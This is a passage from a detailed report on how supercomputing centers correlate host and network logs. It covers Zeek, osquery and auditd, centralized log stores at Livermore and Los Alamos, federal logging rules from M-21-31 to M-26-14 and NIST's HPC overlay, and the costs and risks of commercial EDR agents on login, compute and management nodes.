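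Campbell described the auditd software as an alpha version in 2014. In August 2015 it was a late prototype on one midrange system, and NERSC hoped to put it into full production later that year. *Effective and non-intrusive security within NERSC's Open Science HPC environment* (Singer, 2016) lists host-based data analysis and network monitoring among the center's efforts but does not mention auditd. It is unclear whether the software ever ran on all of NERSC's systems. Campbell does not report how many connections it matched or how many intruders it found, so the work mainly shows that the design is feasible.

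### What zeek-osquery measured

Zeek-osquery connects Zeek to the host monitor osquery. Osquery reports processes and sockets as they appear, and Zeek keeps a list of the active ones. When a connection crosses the network, Zeek looks for a socket with the same addresses, ports and protocol. If it finds one, it adds the host, program and user to the connection log. A process that crashes leaves no audit record of its end, so Zeek also periodically queries each host for the processes that still exist.

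Haas and colleagues tried this for three working days on 11 Linux office machines, which produced 344,366 flows. (A flow is the traffic between two endpoints, whether or not the protocol has connections.)

| Type of traffic | Share matched to a program and user |
|---|---|
| TCP | 96.05% |
| UDP | 50.43% |
| All flows | 86.61% |

Zeek alone identified the program behind only 0.06 percent of flows. UDP flows were matched to host records much less often than TCP flows, mainly because 89 percent of the UDP flows were name lookups, which often finish before osquery has recorded the socket. Host data sometimes arrived too late to match short TCP connections. Other matches failed because a program used an IPv6 address for traffic that crossed the network as IPv4, or because a machine had left the laboratory's virtual private network and another had taken its address.

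Zeek found one candidate process for 88.5 percent of the matched flows and several for the rest. It found a single user for 98.1 percent, but only one person was logged in to each machine, and the other candidates were system accounts. A login node would be a much harder test, because many users may contact the same servers at the same time.

The figure of 870 hosts per Zeek instance also depends on how many events each host sends. Haas and colleagues simulated hosts that each sent four events a second, measured how much of Zeek's processor time each host used, and calculated how many hosts would use all of it. Their real office machines each sent less than half an event a second, well below the simulated rate, but a login node can easily exceed that rate. A compilation that starts 40,000 processes in five minutes produces about 133 events a second, roughly the load of 33 simulated hosts.

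One of the paper's detection scripts looks for people who use one machine to reach another. It would be useful on a login node, which always has many SSH connections in both directions. When Zeek finds an incoming and an outgoing connection on the same host, the script uses osquery to check whether the outgoing one belongs to a process started by the incoming session. If so, one person is passing through the machine. Legitimate researchers also do this, and the paper does not measure how often the script would flag them.

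### Joining the records afterwards

Both of these systems match records inside Zeek as they arrive. A center can instead send Zeek's logs and the host logs to a central log store and match them there. NCSA follows this general approach. *NCSA Security Operations Log Review Procedures* (Withers and Slagell, 2020) states that the center continuously collects system logs and network data, and that automated tools analyze them and notify the security team. Staff review these notices during business hours and can be reached through a help desk at other times.

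Los Alamos similarly uses Splunk to combine logs from its clusters, networks and file systems so that administrators and security analysts can correlate them (Shrader, 2024). Researchers at NCSA plan to have AI agents examine logs from login hosts, GPU nodes and fast internal networks together with scheduler data.

Matching records in a log store can wait for late host data, which caused some of zeek-osquery's failures. Analysts can also repeat a search when they learn of a new hostile address. The drawback is delay. A search that runs every ten minutes may find an upload only after it has finished, whereas a rule in Zeek could have signaled the router to block it.

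Berkeley Lab combines host and network data in Zeek today, but at a coarser level. It uses 50 or more lists, including SSH and VPN logins, address assignments, an employee directory and the inventory of machines that run CrowdStrike, a commercial EDR product. In an example from Sharma and Banerjee, Zeek without the lists logs a connection between two addresses on the Windows file-sharing port. With the lists, the alert shows that the source is an exit point of the anonymity network Tor and the destination is a physicist's workstation that is missing its security agent.

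This works well for a workstation that belongs to one person. On a login node, it would identify the machine and perhaps everyone logged in, but not which of them opened the connection, so a supercomputing center still needs records of individual processes.

### Three months of traffic at Los Alamos

Los Alamos tested how much a center can learn from network records alone. *Cray EX40 (Chicoma) Cluster Intrusion Detection Project* (Wild, 2023) reports on three months of traffic between the Chicoma supercomputer and outside networks. A 10-gigabit mirror port copied the traffic to a separate server running Zeek and Suricata, so the monitoring took no processor time from the cluster. Filters based on eBPF skipped very large transfers.

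Both programs flagged possible password guessing. In the most striking case, a single source made about 1,610 SSH attempts in roughly 12 hours. Wild, McGee and Areba (2023), in *Cray EX40 Cluster Network Intrusion Detection System*, give the period as 14 hours, or about one failed login every 31 seconds. They traced all the failures they examined to users' misconfigured software. Some file transfer programs kept trying stored credentials after they expired, and in another case Git was calling a password prompt that did not work.

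The programs also found four invalid certificates, the files that servers use to prove their identity. Staff had deliberately signed these themselves instead of obtaining them from a recognized authority. Most of the other findings were configuration errors:

- Name lookups made up about 35 percent of the captured traffic, and 97 percent of them were abnormal. One node was responsible for most of these, with about 40,000 lookups an hour for cluster components that did not exist.
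- Nine switches were sending lookups to Google because of a cloud management setting that nobody had turned off.
- The laboratory's web proxy rejected about 37 percent of outgoing web requests. Many were for addresses that work only on a local network, and the software had probably meant to contact its own machine.

The project improved the cluster, but Wild and colleagues report no intrusions. That could mean there were none, or that any intruders had valid credentials and looked like ordinary users. Automatic blocking based on the number of failed SSH logins would have shut out legitimate researchers. Zeek could identify the source of the attempts, but staff had to work with the users to find the cause.

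### Where matching fails

Matching host records to Zeek's can show that a certain program sent 3 gigabytes over TLS, but not what the data contained, because the traffic stays encrypted. Haas and colleagues built a prototype that obtains encryption keys from the host so Zeek can read the traffic. The prototype works only with programs that leave encryption to the kernel, and the collected keys would need protection.

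Zeek also misses connections that do not pass a tap. Oak Ridge's taps are at the main entry and exit points of its network. Berkeley Lab also monitors some internal subnets, because an intruder moving between machines inside the laboratory never crosses the network border. Traffic between compute nodes usually stays on the cluster's own network, where a border tap cannot record it. Staff may have only host records of a login from one compute node to another.

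Address translation is another obstacle. Compute nodes often have private addresses and reach the internet through a gateway, which replaces each node's address with its own. A tap outside the gateway then records the same source address for every job on the cluster. To identify the node, staff need either a tap on the cluster side of the gateway or the gateway's record of which node made each connection.

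The host and Zeek clocks also have to agree. If a login node's clock is three seconds slow, a search for audit records within one second of the Zeek record will miss the right one and may return another user's connection to the same server. Searching a wider time range finds the right record but also returns more wrong ones. Synchronizing all clocks to the same time server largely avoids the problem, as long as someone checks that the synchronization still works.

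An intruder with root can stop auditd, but Zeek will still record the node's connections, so a connection with no matching host record might reveal the tampering. This is difficult to use in practice because many connections fail to match. In the zeek-osquery trial, almost 4 percent of 273,241 TCP connections had no match, or about 3,600 a day on just 11 office machines. A much clearer sign would be a node whose host records stop completely while its traffic continues.

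## Collecting logs from thousands of nodes, and the rules that apply

Staff need to collect all nodes' records in one place to notice when a node stops sending them. Lawrence Livermore National Laboratory had more than 6,000 nodes in over 30 clusters when Garcia-Lomeli surveyed them in 2015. *Monitoring HPC Security at LLNL* (Lee, 2024) describes the system that later gathered their logs.

### From a login node to an analyst's search

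When a researcher logs in to one of Livermore's login nodes, the SSH server writes a line about the login, and the node forwards it over the network. In Lee's diagram, the nodes of a cluster send logs to two Splunk installations. One belongs to Livermore Computing, which runs the machines, and the other apparently belongs to the laboratory's cybersecurity staff.

Livermore also uses Elastic, a competing set of programs. In a typical Elastic system, Beats forwards each log line and Logstash splits it into fields such as user and address. Elasticsearch then stores and indexes the fields, and Kibana displays search results in a web browser. Because the fields are separate, an analyst can search for every login by one account last week without writing a pattern to match the raw text. If several stores hold the same line, an intruder has to alter all of them to erase it.

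In September 2023 the Elastic system had about 112 terabytes of flash storage and 2 petabytes of hard disk. New records go to the flash, where searches are fast, and older ones move to the disks. If the laboratory collected a hypothetical one terabyte a day, the flash would hold almost four months of logs and the disks another five and a half years. A small separate system monitors the main Elastic servers so that staff can still be alerted if those servers fail.

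Livermore's dashboards include charts of log messages per hour, operating system versions, firewall traffic and SSH authentications. Once staff suspect an account has been compromised, they can use the SSH records to find where else it was used, but a chart is unlikely to reveal a stolen credential in the first place.

Lee illustrates the searches with a flood of auditd records that staff had to trace. Searching one day of records took 1.25 seconds, a week took 20 seconds, and November 1 to January 8 took 42 seconds. Staff can widen the period to find out when a flood began and whether it has happened before. These times are acceptable for a person investigating one problem but would be too slow for an automatic rule that had to search ten weeks of history at every login.

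Livermore had expected Elastic to search much faster than Splunk, but Lee called the results "a bit mixed" and saw room for further tuning. Lee also planned to add more automated alerts and perhaps anomaly detection, so in 2024 detection at Livermore probably still depended partly on someone checking the right chart.

### Why one command can fill the log

Each node keeps its own log, so a parallel job multiplies the records of a single action. If a user starts a program on 1,000 nodes with 64 processes on each, and auditd writes five records per program start, that one command produces 320,000 records within seconds. Similarly, when a shared file system stops responding, every node that mounts it may report the same error.

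*High-Performance Computing (HPC) Security Overlay* (Guo, Licata and colleagues, 2025), NIST's draft security guidance for supercomputers, warns that this duplication can slow the system. It advises centers to look for duplicate records and to consider logging fewer kinds of event where the risk is tolerable.

A center could replace the 320,000 records with one full record, a count and a list of nodes. But it has to choose carefully which records to treat as duplicates. If 999 nodes run `climate_model` from the project's directory and one node runs a program of the same name from a hidden directory in memory, merging the records by name alone would conceal the one that needs investigating.

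### When the central store fails

When the central log store is down, a server with a disk can save its logs and send them later, but a diskless node can save them only in memory, which the user's job also needs. A node that reserves 100 megabytes for unsent records and produces one megabyte a minute will fill that space in 100 minutes. It then has to discard records, delay the programs that produce them or take more memory from the job. If the node reboots before the log store recovers, it loses all the records it had saved.

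The draft therefore calls for early warning and a quick response when logging fails, particularly at centers with diskless nodes. It also warns that an overflowing log system can cause other systems to fail. Recovery could also be difficult, because thousands of nodes may try to send their saved records at once. One remedy would be a relay server in each cluster, with its own disk to store the cluster's records until the central store returned. A relay could also fail, but the outage would then affect only one cluster.

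### The federal logging memoranda

The White House Office of Management and Budget (OMB) set detailed logging rules for federal agencies after the SolarWinds incident, in which intruders entered government networks through a compromised software product. Memorandum M-21-31, *Improving the Federal Government's Investigative and Remediation Capabilities Related to Cybersecurity Incidents* (Young, 2021), required agencies to forward logs to central systems in near real time. If logging stopped unexpectedly, monitoring staff had to receive an alert and investigate promptly.

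The memorandum ranked types of log by how useful they are for detecting threats. For Linux, the top category included process starts and ends, commands, file access and active network connections. Centers try to collect roughly these records on login nodes, but recording every file access on compute nodes would use a lot of resources.

Agencies had two years, until August 2023, to reach the highest level. The Government Accountability Office found that 20 of 23 agencies missed that deadline, according to Federal News Network's *OMB revamps cyber event logging requirements* (2026).

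On May 22, 2026, OMB rescinded M-21-31 and replaced it with M-26-14. In *Ensuring Effective and Efficient Agency Logging and Network Visibility*, Vought (2026) explains that keeping vast quantities of logs without a clear use had been neither feasible nor cost-effective for most agencies.

| | M-21-31 (2021) | M-26-14 (2026) |
|---|---|---|
| Logs in active storage or immediately searchable | 12 months for most logs | 6 months |
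| Logs in slower storage | A further 18 months | Until 12 months after creation |
| Choice of logs | Long lists of required types | Logs that answer certain questions, such as who acted, which data they touched and how they gained privileges |
| Time to reach the "advanced" level | Two years | 320 days after new technical guidance appears |

The shorter retention period lets a large center collect much more data each day. If Livermore filled all of its Elastic storage and kept no duplicate copies, it could take in about 2.3 terabytes a day under the old rule and 5.8 under the new one. It could use the extra space to record more kinds of events. But if staff discovered an intrusion 14 months after it began, the new minimum would no longer guarantee any record of how it started.

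The new memorandum also sets inconsistent retention periods. Its baseline requires six months of searchable logs, but its "advanced" level, the highest level that has a deadline, requires only three months.

Another measure fits supercomputers badly. To reach the advanced level, an agency must have its required logs for at least 90 percent of the hardware and software in a system's inventory. Perlmutter has about 120 compute nodes for every login node, and a center with those proportions could not reach 90 percent by logging only its login nodes and management servers. However, the agency decides in its own plan which logs are required, so it could presumably require very little from each compute node.

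### CISA's replacement guidance

The Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA), which helps federal agencies defend their networks, had written a guide to implementing M-21-31. On August 20, 2026, it released a Logging Reference Architecture for the new memorandum, M-26-14. CISA developed the architecture with OMB and a council of agencies' security chiefs, according to ExecutiveGov. The release date determined the memorandum's deadlines. Agencies had to submit logging plans by November 18, 2026, and must reach the advanced level by early July 2027.

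The architecture calls for a different collection method for each type of source, followed by shared processing. According to Help Net Security's *CISA's logging guidance works beyond government*, CISA cautions agencies against letting one analysis platform hold the only lasting copy of an event, and warns that a central store can become a fragile chokepoint. This advice suits diskless nodes because they keep no copy of their own.

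CISA also treats the output of AI tools as derived data that agencies should keep linked to the original records. If Livermore adds anomaly detection, an analyst would still need the login or process record behind an alert to judge whether the alert was correct.

M-26-14 also affects users' privacy. When an agency knows or suspects that someone has compromised a federal network, it must give logs to CISA and the FBI on request, as far as the law permits. If a center logs users' commands, those records could leave the center during an investigation.

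### From 10 sessions to 256

Administrators still have to turn general requirements into settings on each machine. The Defense Information Systems Agency (DISA), which runs networks for the US military, publishes Security Technical Implementation Guides (STIGs) for this purpose. Lee describes how Livermore worked with DISA on the guide for TOSS, the national laboratories' shared Linux system.

They started from the guide for Red Hat Enterprise Linux 8, because TOSS 4 derives from that system. Most changes were small, such as replacing wording that applied only to the Defense Department. A larger change removed the requirement for an explicit list of approved software. Livermore argued that such a list does not suit a system used to develop software.

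They also raised the limit on concurrent sessions from 10 to 256. The original limit is meant to prevent denial of service, where one account opens so many sessions that nobody else can use the machine. A researcher at a supercomputing center can easily exceed ten with several terminals, file transfers and scripts that open their own connections. The higher limit probably doesn't make intruders much harder to detect, since an intruder needs only one session. But a single account can more easily overload a login node, deliberately or through a faulty script.

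NIST came to a similar view. Its draft adds only one control to the standard set it builds on, a limit on concurrent sessions. Centers may choose a higher limit, or a different limit for each zone, after assessing the risk.

Livermore publishes scripts that apply the TOSS guide, and Lee stresses that staff need to check regularly that the settings remain in place. Even if every setting is in place, the logs might not reveal an intruder, because the guide's rules would probably miss some attacks on the kernel.

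### How NIST adapted its controls

NIST's general catalog, SP 800-53, lists security controls, such as keeping audit records or scanning for malware. A baseline is a selection of controls from this catalog, and an overlay adapts a baseline to a particular kind of system. The overlay for supercomputers, SP 800-234, starts with the 287 controls in the moderate baseline, adds one that limits sessions, and gives special guidance or explanations for 60 of the resulting 288.

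NIST announced the final version of its *High-Performance Computing (HPC) Security Overlay* (Guo, Licata and colleagues, 2026) on May 4, 2026. Security staff from national laboratories, NASA, the Defense Department and universities helped write it. Both the final version and the May 2025 draft tailor 60 controls, but NIST may have changed individual provisions after public comment. The provisions below come from the draft.

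| Subject | Draft guidance for supercomputers |
|---|---|
| Malicious code | Scanning processes in real time is the most effective method. Periodic scans of large file systems are often infeasible, and scans from several nodes repeat the same work. |
| System monitoring | Large transfers can overwhelm standard network monitors, and monitoring the internal network needs special care to avoid slowing jobs. |
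| Integrity checks | These apply to system software, not to programs that users install. Regular checks of an entire parallel file system are infeasible. |
| Vulnerability scans | Scanning one of several identical nodes, or one copy of a diskless system's image, may be sufficient. |

The guidance on malicious code assumes that users' own computers have malware protection, which scans files before they reach the center. But a center cannot enforce this on outside users' laptops, and an intruder with a stolen credential can connect from a computer that no institution manages. The draft also lets a center adapt the control wherever it harms performance, so centers could weaken scanning on the compute nodes, where it would be most disruptive.

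The limits on integrity checks are reasonable because a center can detect an altered SSH server by comparing it with a known correct copy, but has no such copy of a program that a student has just compiled. Scanning a single diskless image saves a great deal of work. The scan can find a vulnerable program that every node will load, but not a change an intruder has made in the memory of one running node.

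For network monitoring, the draft suggests inspecting a copy of the traffic, as Berkeley Lab does with Zeek.

The draft is also lenient about long sessions. Making users reauthenticate can interrupt debugging or large downloads, so centers often set the reauthentication interval to infinity. The draft suggests locking the screen of the user's computer as one compensating measure, but that would not stop an intruder who hijacks the session. After the initial multi-factor login, a center may also let users move between nodes under the same identity without authenticating again.

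### Testing the logging order

In HPCwire's *Top HPC Players Creating New Security Architecture Amid Neglect* (2023), Guo explains that separate guidance for each zone can spare centers from applying one rule to every node. Under NIST's draft overlay, the management zone should have the most detailed logs, followed by the access zone, while the data storage and computing zones have the lowest priority. The draft bases this order on CISA's guide to M-21-31, which OMB withdrew 18 days after NIST published the final overlay.

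The order makes sense if the aim is to limit the worst damage. An intruder who controls the configuration servers can change every node, and one who reaches the central log store may be able to erase the evidence. Only administrators should enter this zone, so its logs contain less ordinary user activity, and an unexpected login is a much clearer warning there than on a login node.

Intruders with stolen credentials, however, usually arrive in the access zone and may never enter the management zone.

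| What the intruder does | Where to find a record |
|---|---|
| Logs in with a stolen credential | Access zone |
| Copies the account owner's files | Access zone, and perhaps storage |
| Submits a cryptocurrency mining job | Access zone for the command, management zone for the scheduler's record, computing zone for the program |
| Attacks the kernel to gain root | Access or computing zone |
| Alters system configurations or central logs | Management zone |

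The intruders at NERSC in March 2009 never gained root, so detailed logs from management servers would have revealed little about them. The scheduler's records could have helped if the intruders had submitted jobs, but would not have shown what they typed. The useful evidence came from the servers they logged in to, as it did in Campbell's textbook case.

Centers would do better to give the access and management zones equal priority. A center that followed the ranking strictly could spend its budget on management servers and discover an intrusion only when the intruder reached them. Login nodes are so few that detailed logging there adds relatively little to the total volume. The draft allows equal priority because it tells centers to allocate storage and processing according to the risks they need to manage.

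Computing nodes are a harder case because their number justifies a low priority for routine records, but a process that unexpectedly becomes root on one of them deserves an immediate alert. A separate provision of the draft, which applies in every zone, warns that logging fewer privileged actions may be riskier than summarizing or discarding other events.

A center can also rank logs by type. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Priority logs for SIEM ingestion*, written for organizations in general, puts logs from EDR products first. A center without EDR on its nodes would need a substitute, such as auditd or eBPF records of program starts and privilege changes.

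Even the top-priority zone may not produce detailed logs unless administrators turn on auditing. HPE's *Audit Logs*, from the documentation for HPE Cray supercomputers, explains how to do this for management nodes with a boot setting. If administrators change the setting after installation, it takes effect only after a restart. A center that waits until it suspects an intrusion would therefore have to restart the nodes it wants to examine, which would erase any evidence in their memory.

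### Who has to follow the rules

Vought's memorandum M-26-14 applies to information systems that federal agencies own or operate, and to those that others operate on their behalf. Livermore works for the Department of Energy under contract, so the memorandum appears to cover its unclassified supercomputers. The memorandum excludes certain Defense Department and intelligence systems, and also national security systems, which would include the laboratory's classified machines.

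| Document | Who must follow it | Who may use it as advice |
|---|---|---|
| M-26-14 and CISA's logging architecture | Federal agencies, including for covered systems that contractors run | Other governments and operators of critical infrastructure |
| STIG for TOSS | Defense Department systems that use TOSS, and other sites whose own agency requires it | Anyone running TOSS or a similar system |
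| SP 800-234 | Organizations whose agency or contract requires it | Federal agencies adapting their baseline, and private organizations |

DISA's *Central Log Server Security Requirements Guide* (2024) applies to Defense Department systems and gives its highest severity rating to the rule that the server must enforce limits on who may access it. Such limits are good practice for any center whose logs may contain passwords.

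Most of the advice in SP 800-234 is worded with "should" and "may". Federal agencies have to select and adapt controls from NIST's general catalog, SP 800-53, and the overlay gives them a recognized way to explain to auditors why a supercomputer has no list of approved software. The overlay does not apply to national security systems unless the officials responsible for them approve it. Its use is optional for private organizations, but such advice can later become an obligation. Mondaq's *A New Framework For AI Data Center Security* notes that federal procurement rules already require some contractors to follow SP 800-53.

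A university center that runs its own system with a federal research grant is probably not operating it on an agency's behalf, so M-26-14 would not normally apply. NCSA can therefore discard its detailed SSH logs after about four weeks, as its policy allows. If it ran a system for an agency whose logging plan required those records, it would have to keep them for a year.

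## Why centers avoided commercial security agents

Most of the tools described so far are free programs that a center configures itself or software its own staff wrote. An ordinary company would more likely buy an endpoint detection and response (EDR) product, which collects similar records and can also act on them. Supercomputing centers kept these products off their clusters for a long time. Some of their reasons still hold for compute nodes but are much weaker for login nodes.

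### What an agent does on a Linux host

The term dates from 2013, according to *An Empirical Assessment of Endpoint Security Systems Against Advanced Persistent Threats* (2021). The paper describes EDR as software that collects data from hosts and sends it to a central database, where the product looks for related events in real time. These products rely heavily on rules, although machine learning has gradually taken a larger part. A typical agent on a Linux server works as follows:

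1. The agent runs as root and observes program starts, file accesses and network connections. It gets these events from eBPF, from the kernel's audit system or from a kernel module, which is extra code loaded into the kernel.
2. It compares the events with rules and statistical models on the host itself. It may flag a web server that starts a shell and downloads a program, for example.
3. It sends events to a console, usually in the vendor's cloud, which combines them with events from other hosts and alerts staff.
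4. It kills a suspicious process by itself, or an analyst responds through the console. Many products let the analyst cut the host off from the network, delete files or run commands as root.

The University of Waterloo's *Endpoint Detection and Response* calls such software "necessarily invasive" because it monitors processes, their connections and the files they open. An agent mainly adds two things that auditd lacks, an automatic response and the vendor's knowledge of attacks on other customers. Both would help a center with a small security team. But the vendor's rules may not detect an intruder who logs in with a stolen credential and copies the account owner's files.

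### How small delays add up

The most serious objection is that a security agent can delay an entire job by interrupting one node. A weather model may divide the atmosphere among thousands of nodes, which exchange results after each short time step. No node can get far ahead of the slowest one, so a one-millisecond interruption on a single node may delay the whole job by a millisecond.

Suppose each of N nodes independently has a probability p of being interrupted during a step. One node runs uninterrupted with probability 1 − p, and all N do with probability (1 − p)^N. The job therefore has to wait with probability 1 − (1 − p)^N. The table shows this probability for p = 0.0001, or an average of one interruption per node every 10,000 steps.

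| Nodes in the job | Chance that a step has to wait |
|---|---|
| 1 | 0.01% |
| 8 | 0.08% |
| 1,000 | 9.5% |
| 4,864 (all of Perlmutter's compute nodes) | 38.5% |
| 10,000 | 63.2% |

If each step takes 10 milliseconds and each interruption lasts 1 millisecond, a single node loses only 0.001 percent of its time, but the job on 10,000 nodes loses about 6.3 percent. A vendor could therefore measure negligible overhead on one server even though its agent would slow a large job significantly.

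Jobs with longer steps lose a much smaller share of their time. At the same rate of interruptions, the worst-affected of 10,000 nodes would typically be interrupted about three times during a 10-second step, so the job would lose around 3 milliseconds, or 0.03 percent. Independent single-node runs never wait for other nodes. The formula also overstates the problem if the agents all interrupt their nodes at the same moment, because the delays then overlap.

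A center can reserve one core on each node for system software so the agent does not interrupt the job. On the 28-core nodes in Wilson's eBPF experiment, this would take 3.6 percent of the cores away from researchers.

A delay on one login node doesn't spread to the others because their users work separately. If an agent pauses one of Perlmutter's 40 login nodes for a millisecond, only the people on that node lose that millisecond.

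### Measurements and custom

The probabilities above are hypothetical, and public measurements of a commercial agent on a large parallel job are hard to find. The closest evidence is Wilson's eBPF experiment, which used at most eight nodes. At the probability in the table, an eight-node job would wait in only 0.08 percent of steps, so the test could hardly have detected the effect that worries large centers.

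Much of the resistance to commercial agents comes from custom. Wilson, an experienced administrator, puts the maximum acceptable slowdown at about 1 percent, based on judgment rather than a survey. Wilson also writes that security products can make jobs fail, but gives no example.

Vendor contracts also discouraged centers from adding security software. HPCwire reported that many audience members at the 2022 supercomputing conference complained that system vendors focused on the performance benchmarks in their contracts and ignored security. Dark Reading's *Security Is a Second-Class Citizen in High-Performance Computing* adds that some administrators believed installing their own security tools would breach those contracts. A commercial agent would probably raise the same problem, since the system vendor has not tested it either. Some panelists suggested contracts under which the vendor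 hands security over to the center's staff after a set period.

NIST's working group on supercomputer security recommends measuring each tool's performance penalty (Guo, 2024, *NIST High-Performance Computing Security Working Group*). A fair test would compare the agent with the monitoring it would replace, because free tools also use computing resources. Guo, Licata and colleagues (2023), in *3rd High-Performance Computing Security Workshop*, report that audit services can reduce the computing resources available to users, as they had at several centers. One organization had found a way to limit the effect, but centers often experimented separately and did not share their solutions.

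### Unusual systems and unfamiliar programs

Some centers could not have installed a commercial agent. An agent's kernel module has to match the kernel closely, but vendors tend to support common versions of Linux on common processors, and a supercomputer may have neither. MIT Lincoln Laboratory, for instance, runs a kernel that its own staff modified.

Agents based on eBPF depend less on the exact kernel. Uptycs' *Upgrading Your Linux Security with eBPF*, a vendor page, claims support for Linux kernels from version 3.10 onward and for ARM and IBM Power processors as well as Intel and AMD. If the claim is correct, it answers much of the objection. Staff would still have to test whether the agent works well alongside their center's parallel file system and network drivers.

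An agent can also interfere with a center's existing monitoring. Red Canary's *eBPF for security* warns that once a program consumes events from auditd, they are gone. A second program that needs the same events may miss them. The University of Waterloo advises against running two agents on one machine because each may try to remove the other, or one may deal with a threat that the other is still trying to handle.

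False alarms are a more lasting problem. A vendor can learn that a widely used program is harmless, but it has never seen the program a student compiled a minute ago, so its product may flag it. There is little public evidence on how often EDR products raise false alarms on clusters, so it is unclear how serious this problem would be in practice.

The harm from a false alarm depends on how the agent responds. Killing a harmless process may waste a few minutes on an office laptop, but on a cluster it can end an entire parallel job. If the job had been running on 1,000 nodes for seven hours and had not saved its state, the researcher would lose 7,000 node-hours.

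A center can reduce this risk by setting the agent to report threats without blocking them. This is a sensible way to start on login nodes, though the center loses the automatic response that partly justifies buying the product. Excluding the directories where researchers compile programs would be more dangerous. The attacker in Campbell's textbook case also compiled a program, and a general exclusion would let the next attacker do so in a directory the agent doesn't monitor.

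### Repeated scans and licenses

Traditional antivirus software reads stored files to look for known malware. At 10 gigabytes a second, one scan of a petabyte takes about 28 hours. If 1,000 nodes each scanned the same shared file system, the storage servers would have to deliver the same petabyte 1,000 times.

This is a good argument against scheduled antivirus scans on every node, but a weaker one against EDR, which mainly monitors what programs do. A center can exclude the shared file system from scans on most nodes and scan selected parts of it from one machine. In the draft overlay by Guo and colleagues, NIST prefers real-time process scanning, which supports using something like EDR wherever the performance loss is acceptable.

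Vendors often charge for each host. At a hypothetical price of $50 per host per year, agents would cost $2,000 a year for Perlmutter's login nodes and $243,200 for its compute nodes. Rickey Gregg, who manages cybersecurity for the Defense Department's supercomputing program, told the 2022 conference that money spent on security leaves less for performance.

Not every vendor charges this way. According to *Pass On What You Have Learned* (Lee, 2024), the price of Livermore's Elastic licenses depends on the memory of the servers that store and search the logs. Under such a license, the cost depends mainly on how much data the nodes send. Lee also reports that Livermore was already searching about 1.8 billion records from a single day in early 2024. Detailed records from every compute node could therefore require many more servers.

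### Who controls the agent

An agent with root access on every node gives great power to anyone who controls its console. An intruder who stole an analyst's console password might be able to run commands throughout the cluster without attacking the kernel, bypassing the separation between the access and management zones. The agent may also send researchers' command lines, which sometimes contain passwords, to an outside company. Supercomputers used for classified work often have no outside network connection, so they cannot use a cloud console.

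A center can reduce these risks by running the console on its own servers and limiting who may issue commands, but it still depends on the vendor to maintain the product. Livermore had this concern about Elastic's logging software. Lee said the laboratory chooses products for decades at a time and asked whether Elastic would give meaningful attention to the problems that mattered to Livermore. Lee also reported that operational monitoring of the supercomputers had been better with Splunk, although searches were now much faster.

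Automatic updates create another risk. The University of Illinois' *Endpoint Security, CrowdStrike Falcon, FAQ* presents self-updating as an advantage of CrowdStrike's agent. Self-updating saves work on thousands of different laptops, but it can put a faulty update on all of them at once. On July 19, 2024, a CrowdStrike update crashed about 8.5 million Windows computers. It did not affect Linux machines, but clusters are especially vulnerable to this kind of failure. Their nodes are nearly identical, so an update that crashes one will probably crash the others.

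Centers already have a good way to introduce changes gradually. Operators at the 2023 NIST workshop said they patch and reboot each node when its job finishes, while the scheduler sends new jobs to other nodes. They could update an agent on ten nodes first and wait a day before continuing. On diskless nodes, they could include a tested version in the operating system image. Both methods work only if the vendor lets customers delay every kind of update, including detection data. The faulty CrowdStrike file in 2024 contained new detection data, which the company distributed separately from new versions of the program.

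### Pressure to install an agent

The strongest pressure on US national laboratories came from the White House. In October 2021, Memorandum M-22-01, *Improving Detection of Cybersecurity Vulnerabilities and Incidents on Federal Government Systems* (Young, 2021), directed federal agencies to adopt endpoint detection and response (EDR) and, within 120 days, to find the gaps in their existing coverage. The memorandum defines EDR as combining continuous monitoring with automated, rule-based responses. Auditd alone would not meet that definition, because it only records events.

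The memorandum calls for data from "the widest number of endpoints" and includes servers among its examples. It neither exempts supercomputers nor requires an agent on every node. It requires agencies to plan for license costs and to give CISA access to their EDR systems so that CISA can search for threats. A center that worries about a vendor's access to its machines therefore has to consider CISA's access too. The memorandum does not apply to the Defense Department or the intelligence agencies.

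Centers with National Science Foundation grants have no formal federal security regime to follow, according to Guo, but the university that owns the machines may set its own requirements. The University of California's *Endpoint Detection and Response (EDR) FAQs* states that all university-owned devices should have EDR. Carnegie Mellon University's *Endpoint Prevention, Detection, and Response (EPDR)* requires CrowdStrike on servers, including those used for research. A companion page, *CrowdStrike Falcon EPDR*, dates the rule to August 31, 2023, and says it reflects how much security risk the university's leaders will tolerate.

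Insurers add to the pressure because they commonly ask about EDR on applications for cyber insurance. A university that buys one policy for the whole institution has a reason to grant few exceptions.

Rules for sensitive data, such as health records and controlled unclassified information (sensitive government data that is not classified), can have the same effect without naming a product. In NIST's general catalog of security controls, SI-3 calls for protection against malicious code. Texas A&M University's *Endpoint Detection and Response* names Elastic Defend, the EDR component of Elastic's software, as the university's way of meeting that control. UC San Diego's *How-to* lists an antivirus agent from Trellix and a program that reports missing patches as requirements for the university's research security certification. For an administrator facing an audit, installing a recognized product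 is often easier than explaining why custom rules are just as good.

### Login nodes in 2026

Argonne National Laboratory divided its machines by node type soon after the federal memorandum. *Belated January Newsletter* (Stacey, 2023) told users that CrowdStrike would generally replace McAfee, which the laboratory could not run on Linux. Stacey, whose group manages shared computers for Argonne's computing and life sciences staff, had used CrowdStrike for about nine months without problems. The table compares Argonne's rule with those of two universities. The third row is based on UC San Diego's *SPS Policy on Endpoint Detection and Response (EDR) and Vulnerability Assessment Scanning*, which covers its School of Physical Sciences.

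| Institution | Machines that need an agent | Exceptions |
|---|---|---|
| Argonne | Government-owned computers, including Linux servers and login nodes | HPC compute nodes and incompatible systems |
| Carnegie Mellon | All servers used for university business, research and education | Servers where a contract, consent form or other agreement prohibits it |
| UC San Diego, physical sciences | Workstations, general-purpose servers and public services | By request, for example where an agent slows a high-performance system |

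Only Argonne's rule mentions login nodes, so a national laboratory considered an agent acceptable there. However, the announcement covers the machines Stacey's group manages and may not apply to Argonne's largest supercomputers. Carnegie Mellon's rule seems to cover every node of a university-owned research cluster, since its exception is for legal agreements, not performance.

Berkeley Lab's *CrowdStrike Falcon Information* offers the agent for servers as well as laptops and desktops, but does not show whether NERSC runs it on Perlmutter's login nodes. NERSC has better records than most centers of what users type on those nodes, so an agent would add less there.

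It is no longer accurate to say that centers in general avoid commercial agents on login nodes. The technical case for exempting those nodes is weak, and federal and university rules now favor installing the agents. Without a survey, nobody can tell whether most centers have done so.

### Management nodes

The case for exempting management nodes is even weaker. They run no parallel jobs, ordinary users cannot compile programs on them, and centers need few licenses to cover them. The main objection is that the vendor can control the agent remotely, so a compromised vendor console would give an attacker access to the machines that control the rest of the system.

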